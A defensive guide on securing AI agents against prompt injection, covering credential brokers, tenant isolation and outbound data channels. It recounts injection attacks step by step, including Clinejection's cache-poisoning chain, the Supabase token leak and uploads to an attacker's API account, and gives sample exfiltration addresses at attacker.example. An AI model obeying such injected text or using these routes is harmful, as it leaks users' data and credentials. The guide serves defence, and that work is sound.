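*Agents Rule of Two* (mbgsec, 2025) asks whether writing to the agent's own memory counts as changing state. It should count if a later session with other capabilities will read what the agent wrote, because any text an attacker planted there then reaches an agent that can do more with it.

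### Trusted senders and authors

Untrusted input is probably the hardest of the three capabilities to remove, because the designer has to know who wrote every piece of text. Meta suggests limiting an email assistant to messages from trustworthy senders, such as close friends. But an attacker can take over a friend's account, and a friend can forward a newsletter without noticing its hidden text.

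Filtering by author has the same weakness inside a company. If an engineer pastes a customer's error log into an internal ticket, the ticketing system records the engineer as the author, so a filter that accepts text from employees will let the customer's text through. Meta says the filter should check "author-lineage", which suggests tracing text through such copies, but ordinary office software rarely records where pasted text came from.

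*ROPE* sets a narrower requirement, which may be easier to enforce, on the values that a state-changing tool uses, such as the account number for a payment. Each sensitive value must have "unforgeable provenance", meaning it comes from the user or from someone the user explicitly designated. The agent can still read a stranger's invoice, but it can't take the account number from it. The requirement wouldn't help if an attacker had taken over a designated supplier's account.

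### Limits that Meta acknowledges

Meta says the rule supplements established security practices such as least privilege (giving each program only the access it needs). Meta also says the rule doesn't address agent mistakes, excessive privileges or spam, among other problems. A design that follows the rule can still fail if a user approves a warning without reading it.

The harm from misinformation in an agent's answer depends on what the reader does with it, though Meta counts it among the lower-consequence results of injection. ITPro's *Meta engineer trusted advice from an AI agent* describes an incident in which an employee followed an agent's flawed technical advice, with no injection involved. Engineers without authorisation could then see large amounts of company data for over two hours. Meta rated the incident at its second-highest level of severity, though it told The Guardian that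 "no user data was mishandled". An attacker who controlled only an agent's advice could try to cause the same exposure.

The rule also doesn't suit the agents many people want. The sponsored SC Media article *Operating inside the lethal trifecta* argues that useful agents tend to need all three capabilities, and that pilot projects fail when designers restrict them too heavily. Meta acknowledged in 2025 that background agents would be hard to fit into the rule because nobody is there to approve their actions.

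In September 2026 Meta launched such an agent, Muse, which can read a user's inbox and calendar, run commands and work unattended (Sheasha, 2026, *How We Built Safety Into Muse*). Meta runs it in an isolated environment, withholds real credentials from it, and routes its every interaction with the outside world through a separate component called Sentinel. Meta may regard this setup as the other "reliable means of validation" that its rule allows, but it is too early to say how reliable the setup is. Mathrubhumi, an Indian news outlet, reports that injections occasionally got past the guardrails in tests before launch, and Meta offers up to $130,000 for a successful injection that affects one user.

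### Two designs for the support assistant

The support assistant has to read customers' tickets, so the software company can either remove the assistant's power to act or split the work so that no session has all three capabilities.

In the drafting design, the assistant reads tickets and account records but only writes drafts. A member of staff sends each reply and issues each refund. If checking a draft takes two minutes, checking 500 a day takes nearly 17 hours of staff time. The company also has to stop data leaving through the lookup tool's search log, and staff have to check the case notes as well as the drafts.

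In the split design, one session reads the ticket and fills in a form with the type of request and an invoice number. It can't open account records or send anything. Ordinary software identifies the customer from their login and checks that the invoice is theirs. A second session receives the form and the account record, but not the ticket, and sends a reply to the customer's registered address. The software also has to withhold old case notes and the names customers type into their own profiles from the second session, because both can contain untrusted text.

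A hidden request for ten other customers' contacts would now reach only a session that can't look anyone up. If 350 of the day's tickets fit the form and staff check drafts for the other 150, checking takes five hours instead of 17. Some replies will be worse, because the session that writes them doesn't receive the customer's own description of the problem.

The split design protects much less against refund fraud, because a dishonest customer can submit a false claim with a genuine invoice number and the form will pass it on correctly. The company could reasonably use the split design for invoice copies and account questions, and keep refunds in the drafting design, where an employee can check the payment record before the company pays.

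## Keep passwords, keys and confidential rules out of the model's context

Both designs for the support assistant leave the billing key in its standing instructions. An attacker who controls the assistant's output can make it write the key in a reply, or spell it backwards if a filter looks for the original. The attacker can also reveal or use anything else in the context, so the only reliable way to protect a secret is to keep it out of the context.

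Credentials kept out of the model's context must also be stored where the agent can't reach them. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026), which explains the security of its agents for automating software projects, lists places where a hijacked agent with a shell can look for credentials, including configuration files, remote-login keys, the operating system's records of running programs, and logs. The agent can then upload what it finds or encode it in a public comment.

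A key pasted into a prompt is in the context of every session, and probably in the conversation logs too. A key in a configuration file or an environment variable (a named value that the operating system passes to a program) enters the context only if something reads it. This helps prevent accidental disclosure, but an attacker can get the key with one extra command. *Scaling Managed Agents* reports that Anthropic's hosted agents used to run code Claude wrote in the same container as the credentials, so an injection only had to get Claude to read its own environment.

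### Reading a key and using it

An attacker who reads a key can use it from their own computer after the session has ended, without the limits placed on the agent. In Anthropic's old design, an attacker could have used stolen access tokens (strings that prove a program's right to use a service) to start new, unrestricted sessions. If the agent can use a key but can't read it, the attacker has to work through the agent while the session lasts, and other software can log or refuse each request.

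Docker's *Manage credentials* gives an example of this separation. Docker's sandboxes can connect to an "SSH agent", an ordinary program on the user's machine that holds login keys. Programs in the sandbox can use it to sign data but can't read or copy the private key. A hijacked AI agent could still use it to sign a malicious code change in the user's name.

Hiding a key therefore prevents theft, but the agent can still misuse the key, even without an attacker. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) describes a hypothetical invoice agent that notices a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and pays to renew it. The vendor and the amount may both be within its limits, but nobody authorised it to commit the company to a contract. The damage such misuse can do depends on what the credential allows.

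### How a credential broker works

A credential broker is software outside the sandbox that holds the real credentials and adds them to the agent's requests. OpenAI documents one for its hosted agents, with a GitHub token as the example:

1. The developer stores the token in a vault, together with a variable name, `GITHUB_TOKEN`, and the only host that may receive it, `api.github.com`.
2. The sandbox receives a placeholder under that name. If the agent prints the variable, it gets the placeholder.
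3. The agent runs an ordinary command that puts the placeholder in the request's header, the part of a web request that carries login details.
4. A proxy, which relays the sandbox's outgoing traffic, checks the destination. If the host is on the list and the connection is encrypted, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real token.
5. GitHub answers, and the agent receives the data it asked for.

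Some brokers don't need a placeholder. In Anthropic's current design, when Claude calls an MCP tool, a proxy uses a token tied to the session to find the credentials in a vault, then makes the call itself. For services it recognizes, Docker's proxy overwrites whatever the agent put in the login header.

A service's reply can also expose credentials. When a program logs in, the reply may contain a new access token. Docker's proxy normally masks such tokens, but an add-on can turn the masking off, which lets the real token into the sandbox. A broker should also remove from the reply any credential it added to the request, because some services repeat request headers in error messages or test pages.

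Docker replaces its custom placeholders only in a request's headers, never in its body. If the proxy also replaced them in the body, a hijacked agent could post a placeholder as a comment on a public GitHub issue, and the real token would appear in the comment.

Companies already use this kind of design in production. GitHub runs each agent in a container behind a firewall and routes model requests through one proxy and tool calls through a separate gateway. Anthropic's *New in Claude Managed Agents* announced placeholder credentials as a public beta. It reports that Notion uses them to let agents upload files through its command-line tool without giving the model any API tokens.

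Anthropic treats Git, the system that tracks versions of code, differently. It uses a project's access token to copy the code into the sandbox, then builds the token into the connection back to the project, so the agent can send changes without handling the token. A team copying this idea should check where the token is stored, because Git ordinarily saves a connection's address, including any token in it, in a plain-text file that a shell command can print.

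### Settings and gaps that defeat a broker

The destination check matters most. Anthropic lets developers limit a credential to listed hosts, or allow the proxy to add it to requests for any host the sandbox can reach. With the second option, only the sandbox's network policy limits where the secret can go. Pluto Security, which tested the service, found that the default policy allowed full outbound internet access. Under that policy and the second option, a hijacked agent could send the placeholder to an attacker's server and the proxy would fill in the real key.

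Attackers can also supply their own API key. Willison (2026) describes an attack on Claude Cowork, Anthropic's assistant for office work. Cowork could send data only to approved domains, but these included Anthropic's own API. The hidden instructions contained the attacker's API key, so the agent could upload the user's files to the attacker's account. Swapping placeholders wouldn't have helped, because the request contained none. A proxy that overwrites the login header would probably have replaced the attacker's key with the user's, sending the files to the user's own account.

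The broker creates another risk if it fetches secrets by running a helper program on the user's machine. Docker tells users to keep such helpers, and anything they load, out of folders that the sandbox can write to. Otherwise, a hijacked agent could edit the helper and have its own code run outside the sandbox, where the real key is.

A broker also has drawbacks. Code inside the sandbox can't use a placeholder for calculations that need the real key, such as signing a request. OpenAI recommends keeping those credentials in the developer's own application and offering the operation to the agent as a tool. OpenAI's placeholders work only in sandboxes that it hosts, while Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* says that teams with their own sandboxes can run their own proxy. The team then has to protect that proxy. GitHub counts its firewall, proxy and gateway among the components it has to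 trust, and a flaw in a component that holds many credentials could expose all of them.

Some teams will still have to give a coding agent a readable key. Willison advises them to use keys for non-production accounts with strict spending limits.

### Tokens that expire

A thief can use a short-lived token only until it expires. OpenAI's enterprise guide describes a system that issues a task token when someone gives an agent a job. The token identifies the user and the running agent, and can state the permitted purpose. The software around the agent exchanges this token for narrower credentials, each valid briefly for one service and one kind of action. For example, a credential might let the support assistant read one customer's invoices for ten minutes.

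Ten minutes is plenty of time for an automated attack, so expiry mainly protects against later use. Until it expires, the token keeps working even if someone stops the agent. Revoking a credential doesn't stop work already under way. OpenAI advises security teams to be able to both stop an agent and revoke its credentials.

Products differ in how they handle deleted or replaced credentials, and a team should know the details before an incident. Deleting a credential from OpenAI's vault doesn't cancel it with the issuing service or end a running session. If a developer replaces a sandbox key in the vault, existing OpenAI sessions keep the old one, while Anthropic says its sessions pick up the new value on their next call. Docker keeps a fetched secret for 55 minutes by default before it checks the source again.

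Anthropic doesn't rely on narrow permissions alone, because the designer would have to know what Claude can't do with a limited token, and Claude keeps getting more capable. This is a good reason to put tokens out of the model's reach, but narrow permissions are just as useful then, because they still determine what a hijacked agent can do through the broker.

### Treat the system prompt as public

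The developer's standing instructions, usually called the system prompt, often contain business rules and keys. OWASP, a non-profit that catalogues common software flaws, covers both in its list of risks for language-model applications. Its entry *LLM07:2025 System Prompt Leakage* advises developers not to treat the prompt as a secret or a security control. Even if the exact wording never leaks, attackers can work out many of the rules by sending messages and watching how the model responds.

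OWASP gives the example of a bank's chatbot whose prompt sets a transaction limit of $5,000 a day and a total loan limit of $10,000. It warns that attackers who learn these limits could get round them, but this is true only if the model enforces them. If the payment system refuses anything above $5,000, knowing the limit does little to help a customer exceed it. OWASP makes a similar point elsewhere in the entry, saying that the real risk lies in applications that leave authorisation to the model.

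A practical test for a system prompt is whether the company would mind if a customer posted all of it online. The support assistant's prompt can safely describe its tone, the products and the published refund policy. The other contents need to move:

- The billing key belongs with the refund software, which the assistant calls with an invoice number and an amount.
- The rule about whose records the assistant may open belongs in the lookup software, which can check the customer's login.
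- A refund limit can stay in the prompt so that the assistant can explain it, but the refund software has to check every request against it.

A confidential rule needs more care. Suppose the company lets staff offer up to 20% off to customers who threaten to leave. If the prompt contains this rule, any customer might extract it and ask for the full 20%. The company could instead put the rule in code that checks the account and returns only a specific offer, such as 10%, or no offer. Customers could still learn something about the rule by comparing offers or trying different complaints, and the assistant couldn't explain how the company chose the figure.

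Besides deleting the billing key from the prompt, the company has to cancel it and issue a new one. The assistant has already answered customers while the key was in its context, so a reply or log may contain it.

### Clinejection

The attack on the coding tool Cline shows how far an agent's exposure can extend beyond the secrets it was given. Adnan Khan, the security researcher who found the flaw, published the primary account in February 2026. Cline had set up an automated job in December 2025 in which Claude Opus 4.5 read each new GitHub issue and drafted a response. Anyone with a GitHub account could trigger the job, and Claude had a shell. Khan describes the following chain:

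1. The attacker opens an issue. Its title, which the job copies into Claude's prompt, mentions a tool error and says that Claude must install a helper package before continuing.
2. Claude installs the package, which runs the attacker's code during installation. Claude has no chance to inspect the code first.
3. The code fills the project's cache, a store of downloaded components that its automated jobs share. Above 10 GB, GitHub deletes the least recently used entries, and the attacker puts malicious ones in their place.
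4. At about 2 a.m. UTC, another job builds the nightly test version of Cline. It loads the malicious components, and they copy the publishing tokens from its environment.
5. The attacker can use those tokens to publish a fake update to the main product, because the nightly and production versions share a publisher identity or a package name.

Opus 4.5 had the lowest attack success rate in the open competition, but it installed the package in every attempt Khan made on a copy of the project. The request looked like a routine setup step.

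Khan reported the flaw on 1 January, got no useful reply, and published on 9 February. Cline removed the vulnerable jobs within 30 minutes. On 17 February someone used a stolen token to publish an unauthorised version of Cline's command-line tool. This version was available for about eight hours and installed OpenClaw, a legitimate AI assistant, without the user's consent. Cline found no malicious code in it. *Post-mortem* (Rizwan, 2026) gives Cline's own account.

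It is less certain that the thief came in through the issue-reading agent. Khan called it the most obvious path but could not confirm it. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, recovered a deleted issue from public archives. Someone had opened it on 28 January with a title modelled on Khan's tests, which were publicly visible. That makes the path very likely, but the link to the later theft is still an inference.

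A broker around the issue-reading agent would not have stopped this attack, because the publishing tokens were in a different job, which the attacker reached through the shared cache. The issue-reading job directly exposed only one secret, an Anthropic API key, and its GitHub permissions were already limited. The table shows what each control would probably have changed, based on Khan's and Rizwan's accounts.

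| Control | What it would have stopped | What the attacker could still have done |
|---|---|---|
| Broker for the issue-reading job | Theft of the Anthropic key | Poison the cache and steal the publishing tokens |
| No shell or file editing for the agent | Running the malicious package | Influence replies to issues |
| No shared cache in publishing jobs | The jump to the nightly job | Steal the Anthropic key |
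| Broker for the nightly job | Copying the publishing tokens | Publish through the broker while the job ran |
| Separate nightly package and credentials | Using nightly tokens on the main product | Publish a malicious nightly version |
| Short-lived publishing tokens | Using a stolen token weeks later | Publish while the token was valid |

Khan recommended separate nightly credentials and removing the shell and the shared cache. Cline removed the issue-reading jobs and says any replacement will be read-only with no shell. It also stopped using the cache in jobs that handle publishing credentials. Its releases to npm, the registry that distributes the command-line tool, no longer depend on a long-lived token, because GitHub's build system now proves its identity to npm for each release.

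If Bargury's date is right, about 20 days passed between the injected issue and the fake release. A token that lasted an hour would have expired by then. But the old token would have remained a danger even after Cline adopted the new method, unless someone revoked it. Endor Labs, a security company quoted by The Hacker News (2026), advises developers to disable publishing with traditional tokens when they make this change.

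Cline had tried to cancel the token on 9 February but deleted the wrong one. Its staff checked npm's management page for the organisation, which listed no active tokens but didn't show the exposed one. The next day, an anonymous emailer told Khan that they had working Cline credentials, and he passed the warning on. Cline replied that it had replaced all its credentials. When it replaces a credential, Cline now tests whether the old one still works.

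## Keep one customer's data out of another customer's session

With the billing key out of the prompt, the support assistant's lookup tool can still open the records of all 400 customers. Each customer is a *tenant*, one of several customers or organisations that share a system. A standing instruction to discuss only the records of the customer who wrote in would prevent some mix-ups, because the model would nearly always follow it. But the lookup tool could still open every record, so an attacker who overrode the instruction could get all of them.

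Access control must work the same way whatever the model writes. The database or document store should therefore use the logged-in user's identity to determine which records may enter the context.

### Relevance is not permission

Many assistants find documents by *retrieval*, in which software searches a store for the passages most relevant to a question and adds them to the context. Those passages may come from another customer's contract if it is more relevant than the user's own.

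In *Securing the Agent*, Arceo and Narsing (2026) of Red Hat tested their own open-source framework with three invented tenants, each with 100 documents on overlapping topics. In 300 queries, a user from one tenant asked for another tenant's documents. Without a permission check, 98% to 100% of these queries fetched at least one passage the user had no right to see, and with the check none did.

They also sent 90 prompt injections, some of which impersonated a more privileged role. Without the permission check, 62% of these fetched other tenants' data in one setup and 80% in another, which were lower rates than for plain questions. With the check, all 90 failed. The search had leaked data because nothing checked permissions, and the attacker's wording hardly mattered.

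These figures count what the search returned, and a careful model might not have repeated all of it. Zero leaks here is more reassuring than zero successful attacks in a prompt injection test of a model, because a permission filter is ordinary code that runs the same way however persuasive the question is. The filter may contain bugs, but an engineer can check for them by reading the code. The check added about 19 milliseconds to a search, while the hosted model took seconds to answer.

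The filter has to run on the company's server. Arceo and Narsing also found no leaks when the user's application called the filtered search, but someone who tampered with that application could call the unfiltered search instead. Running the whole agent on the server added about three seconds per answer and roughly halved throughput under heavy load.

### Filter before the search, then check again

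A store that filters after searching takes the closest passages from everyone's documents and discards those the user isn't allowed to see. This protects other customers' data, but it can leave the user with no results, and the assistant might then tell a customer that their contract doesn't exist. Arceo and Narsing fetched five times as many passages as they needed, so that some would remain after filtering. With 100 passages in the store, the first five results contained everything they should have. With 1,000 passages, they contained a tenth of it, and with 50,000 only 0.2%.

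The search misses more when tenants' documents are more alike, and 400 companies asking about the same product may be close to the worst case. Filtering first avoids the problem, because the search then considers only passages the user is allowed to see. A team should test that its own index filters first, since some databases accept a filter in the query but apply it after an approximate search.

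Filtering first works only if the labels are accurate. If someone uploads a document under the wrong customer, the filter will let it into that customer's sessions whenever it matches a question. Labels also go out of date. Arceo and Narsing assume that a document's owner never changes, which is reasonable for a customer's invoices but not for the list of employees who may read a project file. If an employee leaves the project at noon and the index copies permissions overnight, the agent can still quote the file to them that afternoon. The software can prevent this by checking the few passages it found against current permissions just before adding them to the context.

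Some searches also follow links from one document to the next, and a permitted document can link to a forbidden one. *A Survey of Secure Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026) describes a system called Retrieval Pivot that checks permission at every step.

A separate index for each customer removes the risk of forgetting a filter. *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, reports that Amazon recommends either separate indexes or filters on a shared one. Maintaining 400 indexes is a lot of work, but separate indexes may be worthwhile for a few customers with strict contracts.

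### Acting on behalf of the user

All these filters depend on identifying whose permissions apply. Programs often connect to a database through a service account, a login that belongs to the program and can read every customer's data. If an agent uses that account, anyone who hijacks the agent can read all of that data too.

The blog post *AI Agents Security* proposes treating the agent as an outsider with the same access as the user it represents. In its example, an online shop's agent can read the current customer's invoices and search the catalogue. It can see whether an item is in stock, but not how many the shop has. It can make changes only through the shop's API, which applies the business rules and keeps an audit trail. If a user persuades the agent to request another customer's orders, the shop should refuse, just as it should when a user edits the user number in a web address.

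This works well when the user is a customer. A commenter on the post worries about users inside the organisation, such as a bank representative or a developer with access to production systems. *19th June 2025* (Willison, 2025) describes how the security company Cato demonstrated this problem using Atlassian's MCP server. An outsider submits a support ticket containing hidden instructions, and an employee asks an AI agent to process it. The agent follows the instructions with the employee's privileges and can copy internal data into the ticket, where the outsider can read it.

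The agent in that attack acted on behalf of its user. So when an employee opens a customer's ticket, the session should get only the access that both the employee and that customer have. The employee can still look up other records by hand.

*Enterprise AI Must Enforce Participant-Aware Access Control* (2025) applies a similar rule to everyone in an exchange. If Bob emails Alice and copies in Charlie, the system must check all three people's permissions before it gives the model a document. Adding recipients can therefore make the answer less useful. The paper extends the rule to fine-tuning, which is further training on an organisation's own documents. Everyone involved must have access to every document used in the training, because a search filter can't remove what a model has already learned. A company that fine-tuned one model on all 400 customers' tickets would break this rule.

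### Take the customer's identity from the session

Suppose the support assistant has a tool called `get_invoices(customer_id, month)`. The model writes both arguments, so a hidden line in an attachment can get it to enter another customer's number. If the software behind the tool uses a service account and accepts that number without checking it, the attacker receives the other customer's invoices.

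The safer tool is `get_invoices(month)`. The company's software takes the customer number from the login and adds it to the query, so the model can't specify another customer. If the model has to supply an identifier, such as an invoice number, the software should check that it belongs to the session's customer, as in the split design.

This assumes the session is tied to the right customer. Anyone can forge the sender's address on an email, so an emailed ticket shouldn't open account records by itself. The company could send a login link to the registered address and leave the records closed until the customer uses it.

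### Row-level security

Even with a safe tool, a developer may forget the customer condition in one query out of hundreds. Row-level security puts the condition in the database, which then applies it to every query on the table. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, a policy for invoices could look like this:

```sql
ALTER TABLE invoices ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
ALTER TABLE invoices FORCE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

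CREATE POLICY one_customer ON invoices
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer_id')::int);
```

The first line turns on the protection, and the second extends it to the table's owner, whom PostgreSQL otherwise exempts. The policy allows access to a row only if its customer number matches the one the company's software set for the session. A query for all invoices then returns only that customer's invoices.

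The policy can still fail in several ways:

- PostgreSQL doesn't apply policies to superusers or to roles with permission to bypass them.
- A model that writes its own database commands can change `app.customer_id` before it runs a query. The policy above is therefore safe only if the company's software writes the commands and the model just fills in values. An agent that writes commands itself needs a separate database login for each customer, and a policy that checks the login.
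- Programs reuse database connections to save time. If the customer number stays set after a request ends, the next customer's request may run with it. The software should set the number for a single transaction, so that it expires automatically.

Reused connections caused a leak at OpenAI in 2023, although row-level security wasn't involved. According to tianpan.co's *The Privacy Boundary No One Tests* (2026), a cancelled ChatGPT request left data in a connection, and the next request on that connection received the previous user's response. Names, billing addresses and the last four digits of card numbers leaked for nine hours.

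### The Supabase demonstration

Supabase provides PostgreSQL databases and an MCP server through which coding assistants can query them. In 2025 a team at General Analysis showed how a customer's support ticket could turn that server against its user. Willison (2025), in *6th July 2025*, quotes their account:

1. The attacker files a support ticket addressed to the coding assistant. It asks the assistant to read a private table, `integration_tokens`, and add the contents to the ticket as a new message.
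2. A developer asks the assistant, Cursor, to list the latest tickets.
3. Cursor reads the ticket through a database role called `service_role`, which row-level security doesn't restrict.
4. Cursor follows the instructions and copies the tokens into the ticket, where the attacker can read them.

Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) replies that no customer had reported a leak through MCP. It also says that the server may run with higher privilege but doesn't "bypass" row-level security, which remains fully enforced. The dispute is mostly about wording, because the policies were in place but didn't apply to the role the agent used.

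Acting on behalf of the developer might not have helped either, because a developer can often read every table. The task only required a role that could read support tickets.

Willison points out that the server's read-only setting removes the attacker's way of getting the data back. But the agent could still read the tokens, and another tool in the same session might be able to send them out. Supabase agrees that injection remains the main concern in read-only mode. It had wrapped query results in warnings to the model and experimented with classifiers, which reduced the risk but did not eliminate it.

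Supabase's main advice is never to connect an agent directly to production data. A developer building a prototype can use a test database instead, but a support assistant needs real accounts. Supabase's current setup guide also warns that the server can access all of a user's projects unless the user selects one.

### Asana's exposure in June 2025

One customer's data can reach another without an attack. Asana, which makes project-management software, released an MCP server on 1 May 2025 and found a bug in it on 4 June. According to the company's notice to customers, quoted by UpGuard (2025), the bug "could have potentially exposed certain information" to other organisations that used the server. The information included projects, tasks and other material within the MCP user's permissions. Security Boulevard's *SaaS Security Alert* (2025) gives Asana's estimate of about 1,000 affected customers.

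Asana said the incident was not a hack, and UpGuard found no indication that anyone had viewed another organisation's data. But users could have done so for nearly five weeks. Asana notified customers on 16 June, 12 days after finding the bug, and asked them to delete any data they had received that wasn't theirs. Its status page, as copied in IsDown's *Outage in Asana* (2025), listed the outage as "MCP Maintenance".

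The notice says the cause was a bug in Asana's code but doesn't explain the bug. An editor's comment in SANS NewsBites' *Experimental MCP Server Exposed Asana Data* (2025) attributes the flaw to incomplete enforcement of access controls, which could mean a missing filter, a wrong identity or something else. Whatever the cause, a model that perfectly resisted injection wouldn't have prevented the exposure. Asana had logs for each customer's MCP users and offered the logs to customers who wanted to check what had happened.

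### Memory, cached answers and logs

Even a correct database policy doesn't protect data that an agent copies elsewhere. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* describes a hypothetical research group whose agent learns one scientist's preferred crystallography methods and saves them in shared notes. When a colleague asks what the group is working on, the agent summarises those notes and reveals an unpublished project.

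*A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (2026) describes MemLeak, a study that traced leaks between users to searches of a pooled memory that returned another user's entries. Shared memory can also make answers worse without disclosing anything. *No Attacker Needed* (Yang, Li and colleagues, 2026) shows that information valid for one user can degrade another user's results. Memory therefore needs the same customer filter as the original records.

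To reduce costs, some systems save the answer to a question and reuse it when someone asks a similar one. "When does our contract renew?" has a different answer for each customer, so the software should reuse an answer only for the customer who first received it, unless the answer draws only on public documentation.

Logs often hold every customer's text in one place. *Burn-After-Use for Preventing Data Leakage through a Secure Multi-Tenant Architecture* (2026) treats shared logging as a leak to measure separately. If a company lets an agent read the logs to diagnose faults, the agent can see data it couldn't have read from the database. Labelling each log entry with its customer lets the company filter what the agent reads and investigate an incident like Asana's.

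### Shared inference caches

The speed of a model's replies can also reveal one customer's text to another. The software that runs a model often saves its work on the beginning of a prompt and reuses it when another prompt begins the same way. The second reply then starts sooner, so someone who submits a guess can learn from the timing whether another customer recently sent the same text.

Sun and Xiao (2026), in *Where the Savings Go*, tested this on one server at up to half its capacity. For texts of at least 256 tokens, the attacker's advantage (the rate of correct "yes" answers minus the rate of false ones) was at least 0.98 out of 1. An attacker can confirm a guessed text this way, but would need many more attempts to recover an unknown one. *CacheSolidarity* (2026) found that the strength of the signal also depends on the model's size, the load and the hardware.

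Commercial providers separate these caches by organisation, workspace or account. But the software company sends all 400 customers' tickets through its own account, so this doesn't separate one customer from another. Sun and Xiao recommend a separate cache key for each group of users who need isolation. *Mirage* (2026) notes that this loses the savings from reusing cached text that many users share, which here would include the assistant's standing instructions.

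The software company could reasonably accept this risk for its support assistant, because someone who waits for an emailed reply can hardly measure milliseconds. A chat service that displays each word as the model produces it has more reason to pay for separate caches.

### The support assistant with one customer per session

Isolation matters most in the drafting design, where the same session reads the ticket and looks up account records. The company now opens each session for the customer who logged in. Its software adds that customer's number to every query, and row-level security catches any query where a developer left it out. Searches of documents and case notes use the same number.

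The model can no longer retrieve any of the ten other customers' contacts requested in the attachment. An attacker who hijacks a session can reach 1 customer's records instead of 400, and has to hijack a separate session for each of the others.

That one customer's records still need protection, because the hidden text may have been written by someone outside the company. For example, a genuine customer might forward a log file that contains an outsider's instructions. A junior employee at the customer might also ask for contract prices that their managers keep from them, so the software should check the individual user's permissions as well as the company's.

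Some legitimate requests become harder. A consultant who manages five customers' accounts has to open a session for each. The assistant can't search other customers' tickets for reports of the same fault, although it could read a public status page.

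## Close the routes by which data can leave

Even if each session is limited to one customer, a hijacked support assistant can still send that customer's contracts and contacts to an outsider. Willison considers the outbound channel generally the easiest part of the lethal trifecta to remove (*45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*). That is probably right for an agent that never needs to contact anyone, but the channel is harder to remove from other agents because data can leave through actions that don't look like sending, such as displaying a picture.

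### How a web address carries data

A web address specifies a server and what that server should return. Whoever writes the address can put almost any text in the second part. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives the example of a page that tries to make a model open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by something private. Websites commonly log requested addresses, so the attacker can read the private text in the log even if the server returns nothing useful.

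This can happen without a click. When a chat window displays a reply containing an image, the browser requests the image at once, and the image can be a single transparent dot. Messaging apps also request linked pages to show a title and thumbnail under the link.

Looking up a server's name can leak data. Before connecting to a server, a computer looks up its numerical address in the domain name system (DNS), and a lookup for a new name normally reaches a machine that the domain's owner controls. If a hijacked agent looks up `jane-smith-leeds.attacker.example`, the domain's owner learns Jane Smith's name and city even if a firewall then blocks the connection. A sandbox that blocks web traffic should also block name lookups, or leave them to a proxy that looks up only approved names.

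### Five kinds of outbound channel

Outbound channels differ in which computer sends the data. This determines whether blocking the agent's own network traffic is enough.

| Channel | How an outsider gets the data | Does blocking all traffic from the agent's sandbox stop it? |
|---|---|---|
| Direct request | The agent opens an address that contains the data | Yes, if the browsing tool runs inside the sandbox |
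| Rendered content | The user's browser or mail program loads an image that the agent put in its output | No |
| Message | The agent emails the data, or posts a link that a chat service previews | No, if the mail or chat tool runs outside the sandbox |
| Write to a shared place | The agent puts the data in a calendar event, ticket or log that the outsider can open | No, if the tool that writes runs outside the sandbox |
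| Upload to a permitted service | The agent stores a file in the attacker's account at a service it is allowed to use | Yes, but the agent loses the service |

### No network

An agent that edits local files or runs tests with packages already installed may not need network access. Most assistants do need it, but some users will accept a much less capable assistant in return for protection.

OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* describes a setting that restricts what ChatGPT can do. Willison (2026) reported in early June that the setting was reaching personal accounts. When it is on, ChatGPT browses only cached copies of pages, so search results may be out of date or missing. It can't run deep research or agent mode, or download files for analysis, and it may not display images in ordinary replies. Users can still upload their own files.

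The setting doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, and in managed workspaces it doesn't automatically disable connected apps. OpenAI says that data could still leave through those apps or through unforeseen combinations of features. An injection in a cached page can still make an answer wrong.

### Lists of permitted destinations

Many agents need only a few outside services, so a proxy can refuse every other destination. Anthropic's web-fetching tool, for example, lets developers name the domains it may open. Such a list protects data only if no outsider can receive anything at the domains on it, and Willison describes three products where that wasn't true:

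- Google's Antigravity allowed its browser to visit webhook.site by default. Anyone can create an address on that site and watch what arrives. When Willison wrote about it in November 2025, Google listed data theft through the browser as a known issue that it was working to fix.
- Salesforce's AgentForce could display images from a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered the domain themselves and received sales leads in its logs. Salesforce had corrected its list by the time the case became public in September 2025.
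- Superhuman, an email app, could load images from docs.google.com. That domain also hosts Google Forms, which can save data included in a requested address, so an attacker's form collected the contents of dozens of private emails. Superhuman had issued a fix by January 2026.

In all three cases the agent obeyed the list. For each domain, a reviewer should ask who can create a page or form on it and who can read the data sent to it, and should check regularly that the intended company still owns it.

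Redirects can also let data out. Many reputable sites have addresses that forward visitors elsewhere, so a request can start at a permitted domain and end at the attacker's. The proxy therefore has to check every step of the redirect, not only the first.

OpenAI also objects that strict lists produce frequent warnings when people browse widely, and that users may learn to click through these warnings. This is a good objection for a general-purpose browser, but it matters much less for a support assistant that contacts the same four services every day.

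### Uploads through a permitted domain

A permitted service may hold accounts for both the user and the attacker. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes how Oasis Security used this to take data from Claude.ai. The attack began with a link that opened a new chat with a prompt already filled in, part of it invisible to the user. When the user pressed Enter, Claude received hidden instructions to search past conversations for sensitive information, write it to a file and upload the file to the attacker's account on Anthropic's own file-storage service.

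As in the Claude Cowork attack, the upload worked because the sandbox allowed connections to `api.anthropic.com` and the hidden text included the attacker's API key. According to Hackread's *Study*, the service accepts files of up to 500 MB.

When Oasis published the attack in March 2026, Anthropic had fixed the hidden-prompt flaw and was still working on the other two, including the upload route. Luz's account, last updated in May, gives the same status. Oasis Security's later *promptfiction claude desktop technical report* still describes the upload as working on a default installation. A team using Claude's code execution should therefore test the route rather than assume Anthropic has closed it.

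The fix is to check the account as well as the domain. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, an earlier report of the same weakness, suggests that the sandbox should let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account. The same rule would help with other services. For example, an agent allowed to send code to github.com can send it to a stranger's project unless the proxy also checks which project the request is for.

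### Restrictions on what the screen loads

Blocking the agent's network traffic doesn't stop image requests, because the user's own browser makes them. Security researcher Johann Rehberger reported this problem to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. According to his Embrace The Red blog post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft responded that May with a Content Security Policy, a header that tells the browser which sites a page may load images from. OpenAI added a check called `url_safe` in December 2023, but at first left it out of its macOS and iOS apps.

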